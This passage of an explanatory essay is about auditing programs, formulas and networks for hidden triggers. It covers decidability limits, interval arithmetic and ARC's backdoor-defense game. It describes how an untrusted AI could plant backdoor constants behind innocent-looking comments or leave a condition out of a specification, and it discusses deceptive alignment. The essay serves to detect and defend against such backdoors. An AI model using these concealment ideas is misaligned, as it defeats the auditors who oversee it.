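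All these systems need a task that can be scored automatically. For mathematical problems, Georgiev and colleagues usually prepared one in a few hours or less. Preparation can take far longer when the goal is unclear. *Intentmaking and Sensemaking* (2026) describes experts who spent many months working out the constraints and scores that would lead AlphaEvolve to valid solutions. Until they found a missing constraint, a high-scoring program could violate it.

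*What Do Evolutionary Coding Agents Evolve?* (Pelleriti, Nelaturu and colleagues, 2026) examines 121 runs of four systems on mathematical and competitive programming tasks, with more than 10,000 programs in total. The most common edit was adjusting numerical constants. In the median mathematical run, the best program became 1.33 times as long but ended with 1.7 times as many numbers. Pelleriti and colleagues also took 15 programs from the middle of runs and automatically tuned only their constants. Of these, 13 then did at least as well as the final program of their run.

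Much of an evolved program may therefore consist of numbers kept only because they raised the score slightly. A planted constant would be easier to hide among them than in the ten-line loan program. Edits that added an outside software library were the most likely to raise the score, but they also give an auditor more code to check. However, the final program was typically only four to six generations away from the starting program, so an auditor with access to the records could read the changes one by one.

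A high score can also be misleading. Pelleriti and colleagues rescored the competitive programming solutions on tests the systems had not used. Two of the four systems had overfitted on at least 30% of the problems, meaning their gains on the original tests did not carry over.

### Programs as control policies

A control policy is a rule for choosing the next action, such as how far to turn a steering wheel. Reinforcement learning usually trains a neural network as the policy through trial and error. In 2018, Verma and colleagues introduced programmatically interpretable reinforcement learning (PIRL), which first trains a network, then searches a restricted language for a program that behaves similarly. In a car-racing simulator, the programs steered more smoothly than networks and transferred more easily to new tracks.

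VIPER, which Bastani, Pu and Solar-Lezama published the same year, copies a network into a decision tree. A tree trained only on the network's own games may make a small mistake and reach a situation that was not in its training data. VIPER therefore lets the tree play, records what the network would have done in each situation, and trains the tree again. It gives more weight to situations where a wrong move would do more harm. For a toy version of the video game Pong, Bastani and colleagues proved that the tree never loses. The proof covers only the tree, so the guarantee doesn't hold if the network plays instead.

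In 2025, Levi Lelis and colleagues re-examined four papers that had found that programs handle unfamiliar situations better than networks. Networks did about as well after simple changes, such as giving them the same few inputs as the programs or, in a driving task, rewarding them for more cautious driving. If this holds more widely, the main reason to prefer a program is that people can check it.

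Google uses an evolved rule to schedule work in its data centres. According to Google DeepMind's *AlphaEvolve* (2025), this simple rule had been in use for over a year and recovered an average of 0.7% of the company's computing resources worldwide. Google DeepMind also lists interpretability, predictability and ease of debugging among the rule's advantages. A short program could plausibly have these benefits, but Google DeepMind did not report any test of whether engineers would notice a flaw planted in it.

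### The proposal to replace networks with verified code

Max Tegmark, who also worked on MIPS, and Steve Omohundro argue in *Provably Safe Systems* (2023) that powerful AI systems should generally not run as neural networks. They want AI to discover useful algorithms and turn them into proof-carrying code, software that comes with a mathematical proof that it meets a stated requirement. Secure hardware would check the proof and block any code without one.

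They mainly argue that networks are good at learning but have no special advantage once learning is over. A trained network is just one way of carrying out a computation, so they expect ordinary code to do the same job just as well. They suggest that a language model could write this code directly, or that another AI system could study the trained network and extract the algorithm. MIPS was an early attempt at the second approach.

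Tegmark and Omohundro go further and call this the only path to AI that people can control with certainty. They argue that a computer has a finite number of states, so if no proof of a safety property exists, there must be some way to violate it, and a sufficiently capable AI may find it. This reasoning is valid, but the only proof of a true property might be a list of more states than anyone could check, so failing to find a proof doesn't show that a system is unsafe. The requirement also has to be complete, unlike the board-game rules that left out the tiebreak. Their example of a computer that nobody can access without valid credentials is fairly easy to state precisely, but they put off the question of how to specify something like "don't drive humanity extinct".

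### Would a large program be any easier to read?

In *Giant (In)scrutable Matrices*, the forum writer 1a3orn argues the opposite, that neural networks are hard to understand mostly because of what they have learned. The title refers to the common complaint that they are hard to understand because they consist of huge tables of numbers. A model that predicts human writing as well as GPT-4 has to represent a great deal about the world, and 1a3orn confidently predicts that any such model would be hard to interpret at first, whatever its form. 1a3orn adds that matrices are easier to study than the known alternatives for general intelligence, such as biological brains, because researchers can read every number and repeat every calculation.

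The programs that people have actually produced are too small to refute this:

| Method | Typical task | Program length |
|---|---|---|
| MIPS | Adding or recalling numbers in a list | Fewer than 20 lines |
| Decompiled transformer | Finding the most frequent character | 3 lines |
| FunSearch | Constructing mathematical objects | Up to 10–20 lines |
| AlphaEvolve | Mathematics and engineering | Up to hundreds of lines |

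A rough calculation shows how far this is from a language model. The Qwen model that Tan and colleagues partly converted into formulas has about 1.5 billion weights. At two bytes each, they take up as much space as 75 million lines of code with 40 characters per line. Even if 99% of this were redundant, reading the remaining 750,000 lines at 200 lines an hour would take 3,750 hours, or about two years of full-time work. This Qwen model is also very small by current standards. Nobody knows how much a good program could leave out, so the true figure could be much lower or higher.

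How much a network shrinks when rewritten as a program probably depends on what it has learned. Procedures can shrink enormously, as when 16 million lines became three, and a program needs only one symbol to multiply two numbers. Facts shrink much less, since a program that gives the capital of every country needs roughly one entry per country in any language. Such a list might still be easier to audit than weights, because an auditor can search it and check each entry separately. But much of what a language model has learned, such as which of two phrasings sounds ruder, is hard to write as a list.

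1a3orn's objection is mainly about reading programs, whereas Tegmark and Omohundro rely on proof, which doesn't require anyone to understand the program. For example, AlphaEvolve produced a circuit that Google has put into its AI chips, and Google's chief scientist, Jeff Dean, described the circuit as counterintuitive. Google DeepMind reported that AlphaEvolve's changes to an earlier circuit had to pass strict checks that the new version still did the same arithmetic. Engineers can verify a strange circuit this way because they can say exactly what it should compute, but there is no comparable definition of a good translation or a correct reading of a chest X-ray.

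Tegmark and Omohundro's proposal looks realistic for narrow, clearly defined tasks, and machine-checked proofs about software now take much less work than when they made it. But for a general language model, nobody has written the program or defined the requirement it would have to meet.

### Programs that call neural networks

Like the formula that relied on a network's measurements of a chest X-ray, a program can leave the difficult parts to a neural network. Suppose the lender also asks applicants for a letter and has a network score it:

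```
def approve(income, debt, late, letter):
    if late > 3:
        return False
    opinion = network(letter)
    score = income - debt / 2 - 10 * late + opinion
    return score >= 20
```

Every line of the program is easy to read, but the program is still opaque because it uses the network, which could have a backdoor that adds 1,000 points if the letter contains a particular phrase.

The surrounding code can still limit the network's effect on the decision. This program refuses anyone with more than three late payments, whatever the network returns. If the lender also restricted the network's output to values between −5 and 5, the network could change the decision only for applicants who would otherwise score between 15 and 25. An auditor can establish both facts without looking inside the network.

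Several of AlphaEvolve's successes improved a neural network instead of replacing it. Google DeepMind's *AlphaEvolve* (2026) reports that the system cut one type of error by 30% in DeepConsensus, a model that corrects errors in DNA sequencing. It also helped a neural network for managing electricity grids find workable solutions in over 88% of cases, up from 14%. In both cases the network still produces the output, so an auditor who read all the evolved code would not have audited the network's weights.

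### When a model is the author

An exhaustive search tries expressions in a fixed order, so nobody chooses how the result will look to a reviewer. A language model's output includes variable names, comments and layout, which affect how people read the code. In the loan program, a comment such as "correct the balance for legacy accounts" above the line that checks for a debt of 77 might satisfy a busy reviewer.

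This matters even if the model intends no harm. Someone could have tampered with its training so that it adds backdoors to certain kinds of program, or it could find by chance a trick that raises the score and present it with an innocent explanation. In either case the auditor knows little about the model that wrote the program, so the safest course is to treat that model as untrusted.

Tegmark and Omohundro sensibly propose that an AI may write the code and the proof, but not the program that checks the proof. They point to a proof checker for mathematics of only 300 lines of Python, which a person could read in an afternoon. People could then use the checker to verify a million-line proof written by a model they don't trust. The weak point is the requirement that the code is proved to meet. Tegmark and Omohundro want humans to stay in charge of that requirement with help from advanced AI,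 but an untrusted AI could leave out the one condition its code would fail.

Tests need to be independent of the language model that writes the program, because passing tests written by the same model is much weaker evidence that the program is correct. In AlphaEvolve, the user typically supplies the evaluator.

An auditor also can't confirm where a program came from by generating it again. Pelleriti and colleagues took 36 programs that had set a new best score in their run and repeated the exact prompt behind each one ten times. They almost never got the same program, although the new ones typically reached about three quarters of the original score. An auditor could use this variation by generating several versions, preferably with different language models, and examining any input for which their outputs differ. This wouldn't reveal an omission that all the versions shared, as the nine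 board-game programs without the tiebreak did.

The auditor can also restrict what the model can write. If the model may use only arithmetic and comparisons on the applicant's data, it can't write a program that checks the date or contacts another computer, however persuasive the program's comments are.

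## What can be proved about a model in a restricted language

Tegmark and Omohundro's proposal relies on proof because a proof can cover inputs that nobody has tested. How much an auditor can prove depends on which constructs the model's language allows, and a single extra operator can make a large difference. The following formula, for x between 0 and 10, is a useful test case:

y = 2x + 0.000001/((x − 3.7)² + 0.00000001)

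For almost every x, this is very close to the line 2x, which never exceeds 20. But at x = 3.7, the second term reaches 100 and y is 107.4. The term is above half its peak only within 0.0001 of 3.7. A random test lands in that window with probability 0.00002, so 10,000 random tests all miss it about 82% of the time. An auditor would much rather have a procedure that can determine, for any model, whether its output ever exceeds 21.

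### Rice's theorem

A full programming language is one that can express any computation. Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1951 that no algorithm can correctly decide, for every program in such a language, whether the program has a given property, if some programs have that property and others lack it. The theorem applies to properties of what programs do, as opposed to how their text looks. For example, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it never approves a loan for an applicant with more than six late payments. Computer scientists call such questions undecidable.

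The theorem follows from Alan Turing's 1936 result that no algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary program eventually stops. *Undecidable problems* (Poonen, 2012) sketches Turing's proof. If such an algorithm existed, someone could use it to write a program H that reads a program's text and stops exactly when that program would run forever on its own text. Given its own text, H would stop exactly when it runs forever, which is impossible.

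No checker can determine for every possible program whether it obeys the rule about late payments. If one existed, an auditor could take any program A and write a loan program that runs A, ignores the result, and then approves everyone. This loan program breaks the rule exactly when A stops, so the auditor could use the checker to find out whether A stops, which Turing showed no algorithm can do for every program.

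Rice's theorem is about a single procedure for all programs, but an auditor usually has only one program to check. Poonen points out that a single yes-or-no question can't be undecidable in this sense, because either a program that always prints "yes" or one that always prints "no" answers it correctly. However, if a computer can list a set of axioms and those axioms prove only true answers, then any undecidable family of questions includes infinitely many whose answers can't be proved from those axioms.

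Rice's theorem doesn't rule out Tegmark and Omohundro's rule of blocking any code that lacks a proof of safety. This rule blocks some harmless programs but never allows a harmful one. The theorem also doesn't apply to questions about a program's text, such as whether it contains a call to a neural network.

Such limits also apply to some neural networks. Poonen cites a proof by Siegelmann and Sontag that recurrent networks can simulate any computer program. For one set of weights, no algorithm can decide, for every starting state, whether the network ever reaches a certain state. A feed-forward network, like the five-unit loan network, always stops because it passes its inputs through a fixed number of layers.

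### Removing constructs from the language

The auditor can instead restrict the language. The table shows when a general procedure can determine whether a model's output ever exceeds a limit.

| Model | General procedure? | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Program in a full language | No | |
| Program that always stops, with finitely many inputs | Yes | One run per input |
| Loop-free program that multiplies whole numbers of any size | No | |
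| Loop-free program with only linear arithmetic | Yes | Up to one check per path |
| Polynomial over the real numbers | Yes | Grows very fast with the number of variables |
| Polynomial combined with exponentials | Yes, if Schanuel's conjecture is true | |
| Polynomial combined with sines | No | |
| Decision tree | Yes | One check per leaf |

Even with a finite list of inputs, an auditor can run them all, as with the ten million loan applications, only if the program is certain to stop on each one. No algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary program stops, even on a single given input. There may also be too many inputs to run, since three 64-bit numbers have about 6 × 10^57 possible combinations.

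A program without loops always stops. Each run follows one path through its conditions, but 30 conditions in a row can create more than a billion paths. The loan program has only two conditions and uses only linear arithmetic, meaning it adds inputs and multiplies them by constants. A solver can check its four paths almost instantly.

Questions about a program can be undecidable even if it has no loops, provided it can multiply its inputs together. In 1970, Yuri Matiyasevich completed the proof that no algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary polynomial equation in several variables has a whole-number solution. A program could be written to approve an applicant only when a particular polynomial in the inputs equals zero. If the inputs can be whole numbers of any size, no algorithm can determine for every such program whether it ever approves anyone.

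Surprisingly, the problem becomes decidable if the inputs can be any real numbers. Alfred Tarski found a procedure that settles every statement about real numbers built from addition, multiplication, comparisons and logical connectives. It covers the formula with the spike at 3.7. Because the divisor is always positive, y exceeds 21 exactly when

(2x − 21) × ((x − 3.7)² + 0.00000001) + 0.000001 > 0

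and Tarski's procedure can determine exactly whether any x from 0 to 10 satisfies this. The weakness is the cost, which makes the exact method impractical for many formulas with more than a few variables.

Decision trees are much easier to check. If each branch compares one input with a constant, every leaf corresponds to a range for each input, and the auditor can inspect each leaf. A tree with the loan exception would need a leaf for debts between, say, 76.5 and 77.5.

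### Formulas with sines

Symbolic regression often allows sines and exponentials, and some questions about the resulting formulas are undecidable, just as some questions about programs are. Daniel Richardson proved in 1968 that no algorithm can decide, for every expression in a certain class, whether it is zero everywhere. Weisstein's *Richardson's Theorem* defines the class as expressions built from rational numbers, π, ln 2 and a variable x, using addition, multiplication, composition, and the sine, exponential and absolute value functions.

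Sine causes the trouble because sin(πx) is zero exactly when x is a whole number, so a formula over the real numbers can use it to pick out whole numbers. Poonen sketches how to turn a polynomial equation into a formula that falls to 1 or below very close to the equation's whole-number solutions and stays above 1 everywhere else. Deciding whether the formula has such a dip would therefore mean deciding whether the equation has a whole-number solution, which is Matiyasevich's undecidable problem. The dip is like a trigger in that the formula's ordinary behaviour doesn't reveal whether it exists.

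Absolute value is on the list because |f| − f is zero everywhere exactly when f is never negative. Whether a formula is ever negative is already undecidable for formulas built from x, whole numbers, sine, addition and multiplication. For formulas with exponentials but not sine, Poonen reports a decision procedure by Macintyre and Wilkie. It depends on Schanuel's conjecture, which rules out certain numerical coincidences and was unproved when he wrote.

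Restricting the use of sines can also help. In *Elementary functions*, Laczkovich considers formulas that add and multiply whole numbers, x, and sines and cosines of powers of x. If Schanuel's conjecture is true, an algorithm can decide whether any such formula equals zero somewhere in a given interval. The smallest class known to be undecidable also allows one sine inside another, as in sin(x × sin x). A PySR user could rule this out by limiting the expression inside a sine to three nodes.

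These theorems cover formulas of any length over all real numbers. A learned formula with 20 nodes, used over a known range of inputs, is probably much easier to analyze.

### Interval arithmetic

One simple method for a known range is interval arithmetic, which calculates with ranges instead of single numbers. If a is between 1 and 2 and b is between 3 and 5, then a + b is between 4 and 7, and a − b is between −4 and −1. For the second term of the example formula, the calculation goes like this:

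| Expression | Lowest | Highest |
|---|---|---|
| x | 0 | 10 |
| x − 3.7 | −3.7 | 6.3 |
| (x − 3.7)² | 0 | 39.69 |
| (x − 3.7)² + 0.00000001 | 0.00000001 | 39.69000001 |
| 0.000001 divided by the line above | about 0.000000025 | 100 |

A single pass therefore finds the peak of 100 that 10,000 random tests would probably miss. Adding 2x, which is between 0 and 20, gives an upper bound of 120 for y.

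The true maximum is about 107.4. The bound is too high because interval arithmetic ignores that both terms use the same x. The term 2x is 20 only at x = 10, where the spike is almost zero. Kronberger, de Franca and colleagues (2021) give a simple example in *Shape-constrained Symbolic Regression*. For x between 0 and 1, interval arithmetic puts x − x between −1 and 1, although it is always 0. The bounds for the spike are exact because x appears in it only once.

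An upper bound of 120 does not rule out values of y above 21, as a bound of 20 would have, so the auditor has to look further. One way is to halve the range repeatedly and keep only the pieces whose bound is above 21. After 15 rounds and 34 interval calculations, this leaves a stretch about 0.0006 wide around 3.7, where one ordinary test confirms that y exceeds 21.

The way a formula is written also affects the result. Dick (2017), in *Interval Arithmetic and Interval-Aware Operators for Genetic Programming*, gives the usual rules, under which division is undefined if the divisor's range includes zero. If the square is written as (x − 3.7) × (x − 3.7), the multiplication rule gives it a range of −23.31 to 39.69, and the method reports a possible division by zero, although none can occur. The false alarm disappears once the auditor cuts the range of x into pieces narrower than 0.0002.

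Neural networks can be analyzed in the same way, but their bounds are often much looser. In the loan formula, the term for the exception is 1000 × max(0, 1 − |debt − 77|). For debts from 0 to 999, interval arithmetic gives its exact range, 0 to 1,000. In the loan network, units 3, 4 and 5 compute the same term, but debt enters the calculation three times, so the bounds become −1,844,000 and 1,844,000. The formula therefore has an advantage here even if no one reads it. Splitting the range of debts would tighten the network's bounds but require more calculation.

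### Approximate answers with a guarantee

Gao, Avigad and Clarke (2012), in *δ-Complete Decision Procedures for Satisfiability over the Reals*, avoid undecidability by slightly changing the question. The user gives a range for each variable, a condition, and a small tolerance δ. The procedure returns "unsat" if no point in the range meets the condition, or "δ-sat" if some point meets the condition loosened by δ. If both are true, it may return either answer.

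If δ is 0.001 and an auditor asks whether y ever reaches 21, the procedure must return "δ-sat". For 108 it must return "unsat", and for 107.4005, just above the true maximum, it may return either. Allowing either answer in borderline cases makes the problem decidable even for formulas with sines and exponentials. The problem is still NP-complete for these formulas, so no known method is always fast.

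The tolerance can cause false alarms, but it can't cause a trigger to be missed, because "unsat" means that the original condition can't be satisfied. Gao and colleagues argue that the false alarms are also useful, because a system shouldn't be considered safe if a tiny change would make it unsafe.

The proof that the problem is decidable uses a grid of test points. The procedure calculates from the formula how close together the points must be for the output to change by less than δ/4 between neighboring points, then checks every point. The example formula has a maximum slope of about 650,000, so with δ at 0.001 the grid would need about 26 billion points. Someone who could run the model but not see the formula could not know that the grid had to be so fine.

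Practical solvers instead use interval methods to discard large parts of the range, much like the repeated halving above. *Descriptive Control Theory* (2014) describes one of them, dReal, which also produces a logical proof that other software can use to check each answer.

### Checking formulas during the search

Symbolic regression can run these checks on every candidate formula. According to Kronberger and colleagues, Keijzer first proposed using interval arithmetic this way in 2003, to reject formulas that might divide by zero or take the logarithm of a negative number.

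The older solution was "protected" division, which returns a fixed value, usually 1, if the divisor is zero. Dick notes that the search often exploits this special case to fit the training data better, which makes the fit to new data worse. Protected division can also conceal a trigger. Most readers would simplify 1000 × ((debt − debt)/(debt − 77)) to zero, but with protected division it equals 1000 at a debt of 77.

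Dick tested the alternatives on a simple target, x₁ to the power x₂, using 20 training points with both variables between 0 and 1. With ordinary division and logarithms and no interval checks, 82 of 100 runs failed to find a meaningful solution. Several runs without interval checks found a formula equivalent or nearly equivalent to exp(log(x₁) × x₂). This formula matches the target except at x₁ = 0, where it is undefined, and no training point in those runs had x₁ = 0. Interval arithmetic rejects the formula regardless of the training data.

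Kronberger and colleagues extended the checks to a formula's shape, so that a user can require, for example, that the output never fall as some input rises. The software computes the formula's derivative, bounds it with interval arithmetic, and gives the worst possible score to any formula that might break the rule. The example formula would fail because y drops steeply just after 3.7. The loan formula would fail a rule that more debt must never help an applicant, because raising debt from 76 to 77 adds almost 1,000 points.

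This is useful for auditing because the user doesn't have to guess where a trigger might be. But it wouldn't catch every trigger. For example, a bonus for all incomes above 777 would satisfy a rule that more income never hurts.

Shape rules also made the search slower and usually less accurate. Kronberger and colleagues compared three search methods with and without rules on 42 test problems, 19 of which were noisy versions of others. With the rules, two of the methods took about five times as long and had higher errors, one on 27 of the problems and the other on 32. But without the rules, none of the methods reliably found formulas that obeyed them. Błądek and Krawiec instead used a solver to find inputs for which a formula broke a rule, and added those inputs to the training data.

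### Trees, linear scores, rule lists and networks

If a model always stops and has finitely many inputs, every question about its outputs is decidable, whether it is a formula or a feed-forward network. Models differ in how much computation the answers take. Barceló and colleagues compared three classes of model on four questions, using yes/no inputs. The classes included decision diagrams, which are decision trees whose branches can rejoin, and linear scores, which add up weighted inputs and compare the total with a threshold.

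| Question | Decision diagrams | Linear scores | Multilayer networks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Can changing at most k inputs reverse this decision? | Fast | Fast | NP-complete |
| Do some k or fewer inputs settle this decision by themselves? | NP-complete | Fast | Σ₂ᵖ-complete |
| Do these particular inputs settle this decision? | Fast | Fast | coNP-complete |
| With some inputs fixed, how many cases does the model accept? | Fast | #P-complete | #P-complete |

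"Fast" means the time grows no faster than some fixed power of the model's size. All the other entries are believed to take far more time in the worst case. Σ₂ᵖ-complete problems are probably harder than NP-complete ones, and #P-complete problems are probably harder still.

None of the questions is easier to answer for networks than for linear scores or decision diagrams. Linear scores are easier than decision diagrams on the second question and harder on the fourth. Even on the fourth, a standard method quickly counts the cases a linear score accepts if its weights are small whole numbers, and a fast method can approximate the count otherwise. Barceló and colleagues show that networks generally lack both shortcuts.

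These are worst-case results, and many individual networks, including the one for loans, are easy to analyze. Barceló and colleagues acknowledge that the ranking depends on the choice of questions and that their work doesn't measure human understanding.

Combining simple models can remove their advantage. *What makes an Ensemble (Un) Interpretable?* (Bassan, Amir and colleagues, 2025) studies ensembles, in which several models vote on each decision. Even with two linear scores, deciding whether a given set of inputs settles the outcome is coNP-complete. The proof uses the hard problem of finding numbers in a list that add up to an exact total. If the total must be 500, one score can check that it is at least 500 and the other that it is at most 500, so both vote yes only when it is exactly 500. A trigger could depend on an exact total in this way.

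Combined trees are easier to analyze, at least when there are few of them. For a fixed number of trees, Bassan and colleagues found fast methods for four of the five questions they studied. The running time grows roughly as the number of leaves per tree raised to the power of the number of trees. Three trees with 100 leaves each have a million combinations of leaves, whereas 100 trees with ten leaves each have 10^100. Bassan and colleagues therefore recommend a few deep trees over many shallow ones, although each shallow tree is easier to read.

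Rule lists, which Rudin favours for their readability, are harder to analyze than trees of the same size. In *Explaining Decisions in ML Models*, Ordyniak, Paesani and colleagues (2025) study how hard it is to find a set of inputs that guarantees a decision and contains no unnecessary ones. This can be done quickly for a single tree but is coNP-hard for a single rule list, even if every rule is short. The difficulty comes from the number of rules, so Rudin's three-rule list for predicting arrests is easy to analyze.

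The comparison is somewhat unfair to rule lists, because a tree for the same decisions can be far larger. Suppose a model has 40 yes/no inputs in 20 pairs and approves a case if both inputs in any pair are "yes". A list needs 20 short rules and a default, while a tree needs more than a million leaves.

The auditor may also want to ignore inputs that could never occur. *Hard to Explain* (Amir, Bassan and Katz, 2024) shows that this can make even a decision tree hard to analyze. For a tree that distinguishes images of the digits 0 and 1, finding the pixels that determine its decision is fast if any combination of pixels is allowed. But if only realistic digits are allowed, the auditor needs a second model to recognize them, and when that model is a neural network, the task becomes NP-hard. A lender can avoid this problem by using simple limits, such as a maximum debt, and checking every application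 within them.

### Real numbers and computer numbers

Tarski's procedure and the algebra above apply to exact real numbers, but computers store most numbers to a limited precision and round after almost every step. A property proved for the exact formula may therefore not hold for the program that evaluates it.

Interval arithmetic proved that y never exceeds 120 in the example formula, but a computer using the standard 16-bit number format can return infinity. In that format, 0.00000001 is too small to store and becomes zero, so the divisor is zero when x is the stored value of 3.7.

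Rounding can also create behaviour that the algebra rules out. The expression (x + 10^16) − 10^16 − x is zero for every real number. In ordinary 64-bit arithmetic, the representable numbers just above 10^16 are two apart, so the expression gives −1 for x = 1 and 1 for x = 3. If a loan-scoring formula included this expression multiplied by 1,000, the rounding error could decide an application, even though a proof over the real numbers would correctly treat the term as zero. Entrants in underhanded programming contests have exploited rounding.

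Undefined results cause a different problem. Computers represent a result such as 0/0 or infinity minus infinity as NaN ("not a number"), and every test of whether NaN is larger or smaller than something is false. The loan program approves an applicant if the score is at least 20, so it would refuse one whose score was NaN. A version that refused scores below 20 and approved the rest would make the same decision for every real-number score, but it would approve the applicant whose score was NaN.

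Gao and colleagues describe two common remedies for rounding errors, using exact arithmetic or validating the results separately. Both are usually hard to implement. In the computer-checked proof of the Kepler conjecture, which concerns the densest way to stack spheres, the hardest computational part was validating the numerical calculations.

Interval arithmetic can also help here, and *Using Shape Constraints for Improving Symbolic Regression Models* (2021) notes that it is commonly used to deal with rounding errors. The software rounds every lower bound down and every upper bound up. For basic arithmetic, the bounds then include the rounded result, provided the deployed program performs the same operations in the same order and number format. In the 16-bit case, the range for the divisor would include zero, so the method would detect the possible division by zero.

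One advantage of limited precision is that it makes the number of inputs finite. 32-bit arithmetic has only about 1.1 billion values of x between 0 and 10, so an auditor could run the example formula on all of them and be certain to find the spike. 64-bit arithmetic has about 4.6 × 10^18, far too many to try on an ordinary computer.

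## When a hidden trigger can be detected: decision trees, formulas and circuits

To prove that a model is safe, an auditor has to say what the model must never do, which is difficult when nobody knows what behaviour to look for. In *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation*, Paul Christiano, Jacob Hilton, Victor Lecomte and Mark Xu of the Alignment Research Center (ARC) study the task of deciding whether a given input is a trigger, which needs no such statement. This is easy for small decision trees with evenly spread inputs but, under certain cryptographic assumptions, infeasible for circuits.

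### The game

Every model in the game answers yes or no, and every input is a string of n yes/no values. Both players know which class of models is in use, such as all decision trees with at most 1,000 leaves. The game has four moves:

1. The attacker, who knows the defender's method, chooses an original function from the class and a probability distribution for the inputs.
2. Chance picks the trigger by drawing one input from that distribution.
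3. The attacker chooses an altered function from the same class. It must give the opposite answer on the trigger, and a random input may have a probability of at most ε of getting a different answer from the two functions.
4. A coin flip decides whether the defender receives the original function with a new random input or the altered function with the trigger. The defender has to say which.

The defender sees only one of the two functions, but can read all of it and run it on as many random inputs as time allows. Guessing wins half the time. A class of functions is defendable if some method wins almost every time, whatever the attacker does.

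Suppose the original function is the loan rule without its exception, and a randomly drawn applicant has an income of 10, a debt of 77 and six late payments. If all ten million possible applications are equally likely, an exception for every debt of 77 changes at most one decision in a thousand, while an exception for this exact combination changes one in ten million. A smaller ε helps the defender because it forces the attacker to choose a more unusual function.

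### Why chance picks the trigger

The game would be hopeless for the defender if the attacker knew the trigger from the start. Suppose each rule in a class approves exactly one applicant and refuses everyone else. The attacker could choose an original rule that approves the trigger applicant and an altered rule that approves some other random applicant. Whichever way the coin landed, the defender would see a rule that approves one random applicant, along with an unrelated applicant whom the rule almost certainly refuses, so no method could do better than guessing. In effect, the attacker would have removed an existing backdoor instead of adding one.

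In the actual game, the attacker must choose the original rule before the trigger is drawn at random. The trigger is then almost certainly an applicant whom the original rule refuses, so the altered rule has to approve that applicant and nobody else. The defender wins nearly every time by raising the alarm whenever the rule approves that applicant.

Real attackers can often choose their trigger. For example, an accomplice might be able to arrange a debt of exactly 77. The game is more realistic if the accomplice's application is already fixed and the attacker has to adapt the rule to it. *Backdoors as an analogy for deceptive alignment*, ARC's less technical account of the work, acknowledges that an attacker without any constraint always wins, but that any particular constraint may be unrealistic.

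### A defender with unlimited time

If computing time is unlimited, the defender's chances depend almost entirely on ε and on how flexible the class is. The standard measure of flexibility is the Vapnik–Chervonenkis (VC) dimension, the size of the largest set of inputs on which the class can produce every possible pattern of answers.

For example, rules of the form "approve if income is at least t" have a VC dimension of 1, because t can be set to approve or refuse any single income, but not to approve the lower of two incomes and refuse the higher one. Rules of the form "approve if income is between a and b" have a VC dimension of 2, because none can approve the lowest and highest of three incomes but refuse the middle one. Linear scores with three numerical inputs, like the ordinary loan rule, have a VC dimension of 4.

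Christiano and colleagues prove that if the VC dimension is d, the defender has a method that wins with probability at least 1 − 15dε, and that no method can guarantee a probability above 1 − (d − 1)ε/2 or one half, whichever is larger. If ε is one in a million, the defender can win at least 99.994% of the time when d is 4, but cannot guarantee better than chance when d is slightly over a million.

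The defender wins by training a replacement for the given function. With ε at one in a million, the defender draws about 200,000 random inputs, records the given function's outputs, and learns a new function from them. The defender then evaluates the new function on the input in question. The defender repeats this several times with new samples and flags the input if the majority output differs from the given function's output.

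This works because each sample is so small that it probably includes nothing the attacker changed. If the alteration affects one input in a million, a sample of 200,000 inputs misses it about 82% of the time. The replacement then learns only from the original behaviour, so it probably gives the original answer on the trigger.

The same effect can drop the exception at 77 from a distilled formula. But in the game, the defender compares the replacement with the given function on the input in question, so the missing exception shows up as a difference between their outputs. A lender could similarly run a distilled formula alongside its network and have a person review every application on which the two outputs differ. Most of these differences would probably be ordinary approximation errors.

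The method is less convincing if training itself produced the hidden behaviour. ARC studies the game partly because an AI system might behave well during training and differently afterwards, which researchers call deceptive alignment. *Backdoors as an analogy for deceptive alignment* warns that training a new model from scratch could recreate the problem.

### Short models and long constants

Short models have an advantage here, because a class of models that can each be described in b bits has a VC dimension of at most b. The 2^b possible descriptions give at most 2^b functions, and producing every pattern of answers on d inputs takes 2^d functions.

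The ten-line loan program has 233 characters, or 1,864 bits at eight bits per character. The class of all yes/no programs of that length therefore has a VC dimension of at most 1,864. If ε is one in a million, a defender with unlimited computing time can win with probability at least 97%.

By comparison, the 1.5 billion weights of the Qwen model that Tan and colleagues studied take up 24 billion bits. Getting the same guarantee from description length alone would require an ε of about one in 13 trillion. The comparison is rough, partly because Qwen produces text instead of yes/no answers. *Backdoors as an analogy for deceptive alignment* also puts a network's VC dimension closer to its number of weights, which would still be about 800,000 times the limit for the program.

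The description has to include every digit of the constants. PySR counts a constant as one node however many digits it has, so sin(c × x) has only four nodes. But if c can have unlimited digits, a rule that approves whenever sin(c × x) is positive can produce any pattern of answers on the inputs 1, 2, 4, 8 and so on, which means its VC dimension is infinite.

Suppose someone wants the rule to refuse 1, approve 2 and 4, and refuse 8. Setting c to 2π × 0.59375 does this:

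| x | 0.59375 × x | Part after the decimal point | Sine | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.59375 | 0.59375 | Negative | Refuse |
| 2 | 1.1875 | 0.1875 | Positive | Approve |
| 4 | 2.375 | 0.375 | Positive | Approve |
| 8 | 4.75 | 0.75 | Negative | Refuse |

In binary, 0.59375 is 0.10011. Each doubling of x moves the digits one place to the left, and the sine is negative if the first digit after the point is 1 and positive if it is 0. The first four digits therefore encode the four decisions, and each further decision needs one more digit. The last 1 only keeps the sine from being exactly zero.

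A 64-bit constant allows at most 2^64 different rules, so the VC dimension is at most 64. An auditor comparing models by size should therefore count bits as well as nodes. Rounding the constants to a few digits, if the model remains accurate enough, also gives an attacker fewer functions to choose from.

### Learning within a time limit

The learning method behind the general guarantee takes exponential time, which is unrealistic for a defender, so Christiano and colleagues also consider defenders limited to polynomial time (at most some fixed power of the problem's size). They call a class efficiently defendable if such a defender can reach any desired confidence below certainty when ε is small enough. The required ε may shrink only polynomially as the inputs get longer or the desired confidence rises.

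Every efficiently learnable class is also efficiently defendable. A class is efficiently learnable, in the standard "probably approximately correct" sense, if a polynomial-time algorithm can take random examples of any function in the class, under any distribution of inputs, and almost always produce a close approximation. The defender can use this algorithm to train the replacements. Linear scores are efficiently learnable, so they are efficiently defendable.

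Defence can also be easy for a class of functions that no fast algorithm can learn from examples. One such class consists of 2^n functions with random outputs. Any two of them differ on about half of all inputs, so the attacker cannot replace one with another without changing more outputs than is permitted.

Christiano and colleagues then allow each function one exception, written separately from the rest, like the line that checks for a debt of 77. The attacker can now always make a permitted change, but the defender only has to check whether the exception names the given input. The example is slightly artificial, and the proof assumes that programs can look up answers in a huge shared table of random bits. But it does show how much detection can depend on the way a function is written, since the check would not work if the attacker could blend the exception into the rest of the code.

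### Circuits and obfuscation

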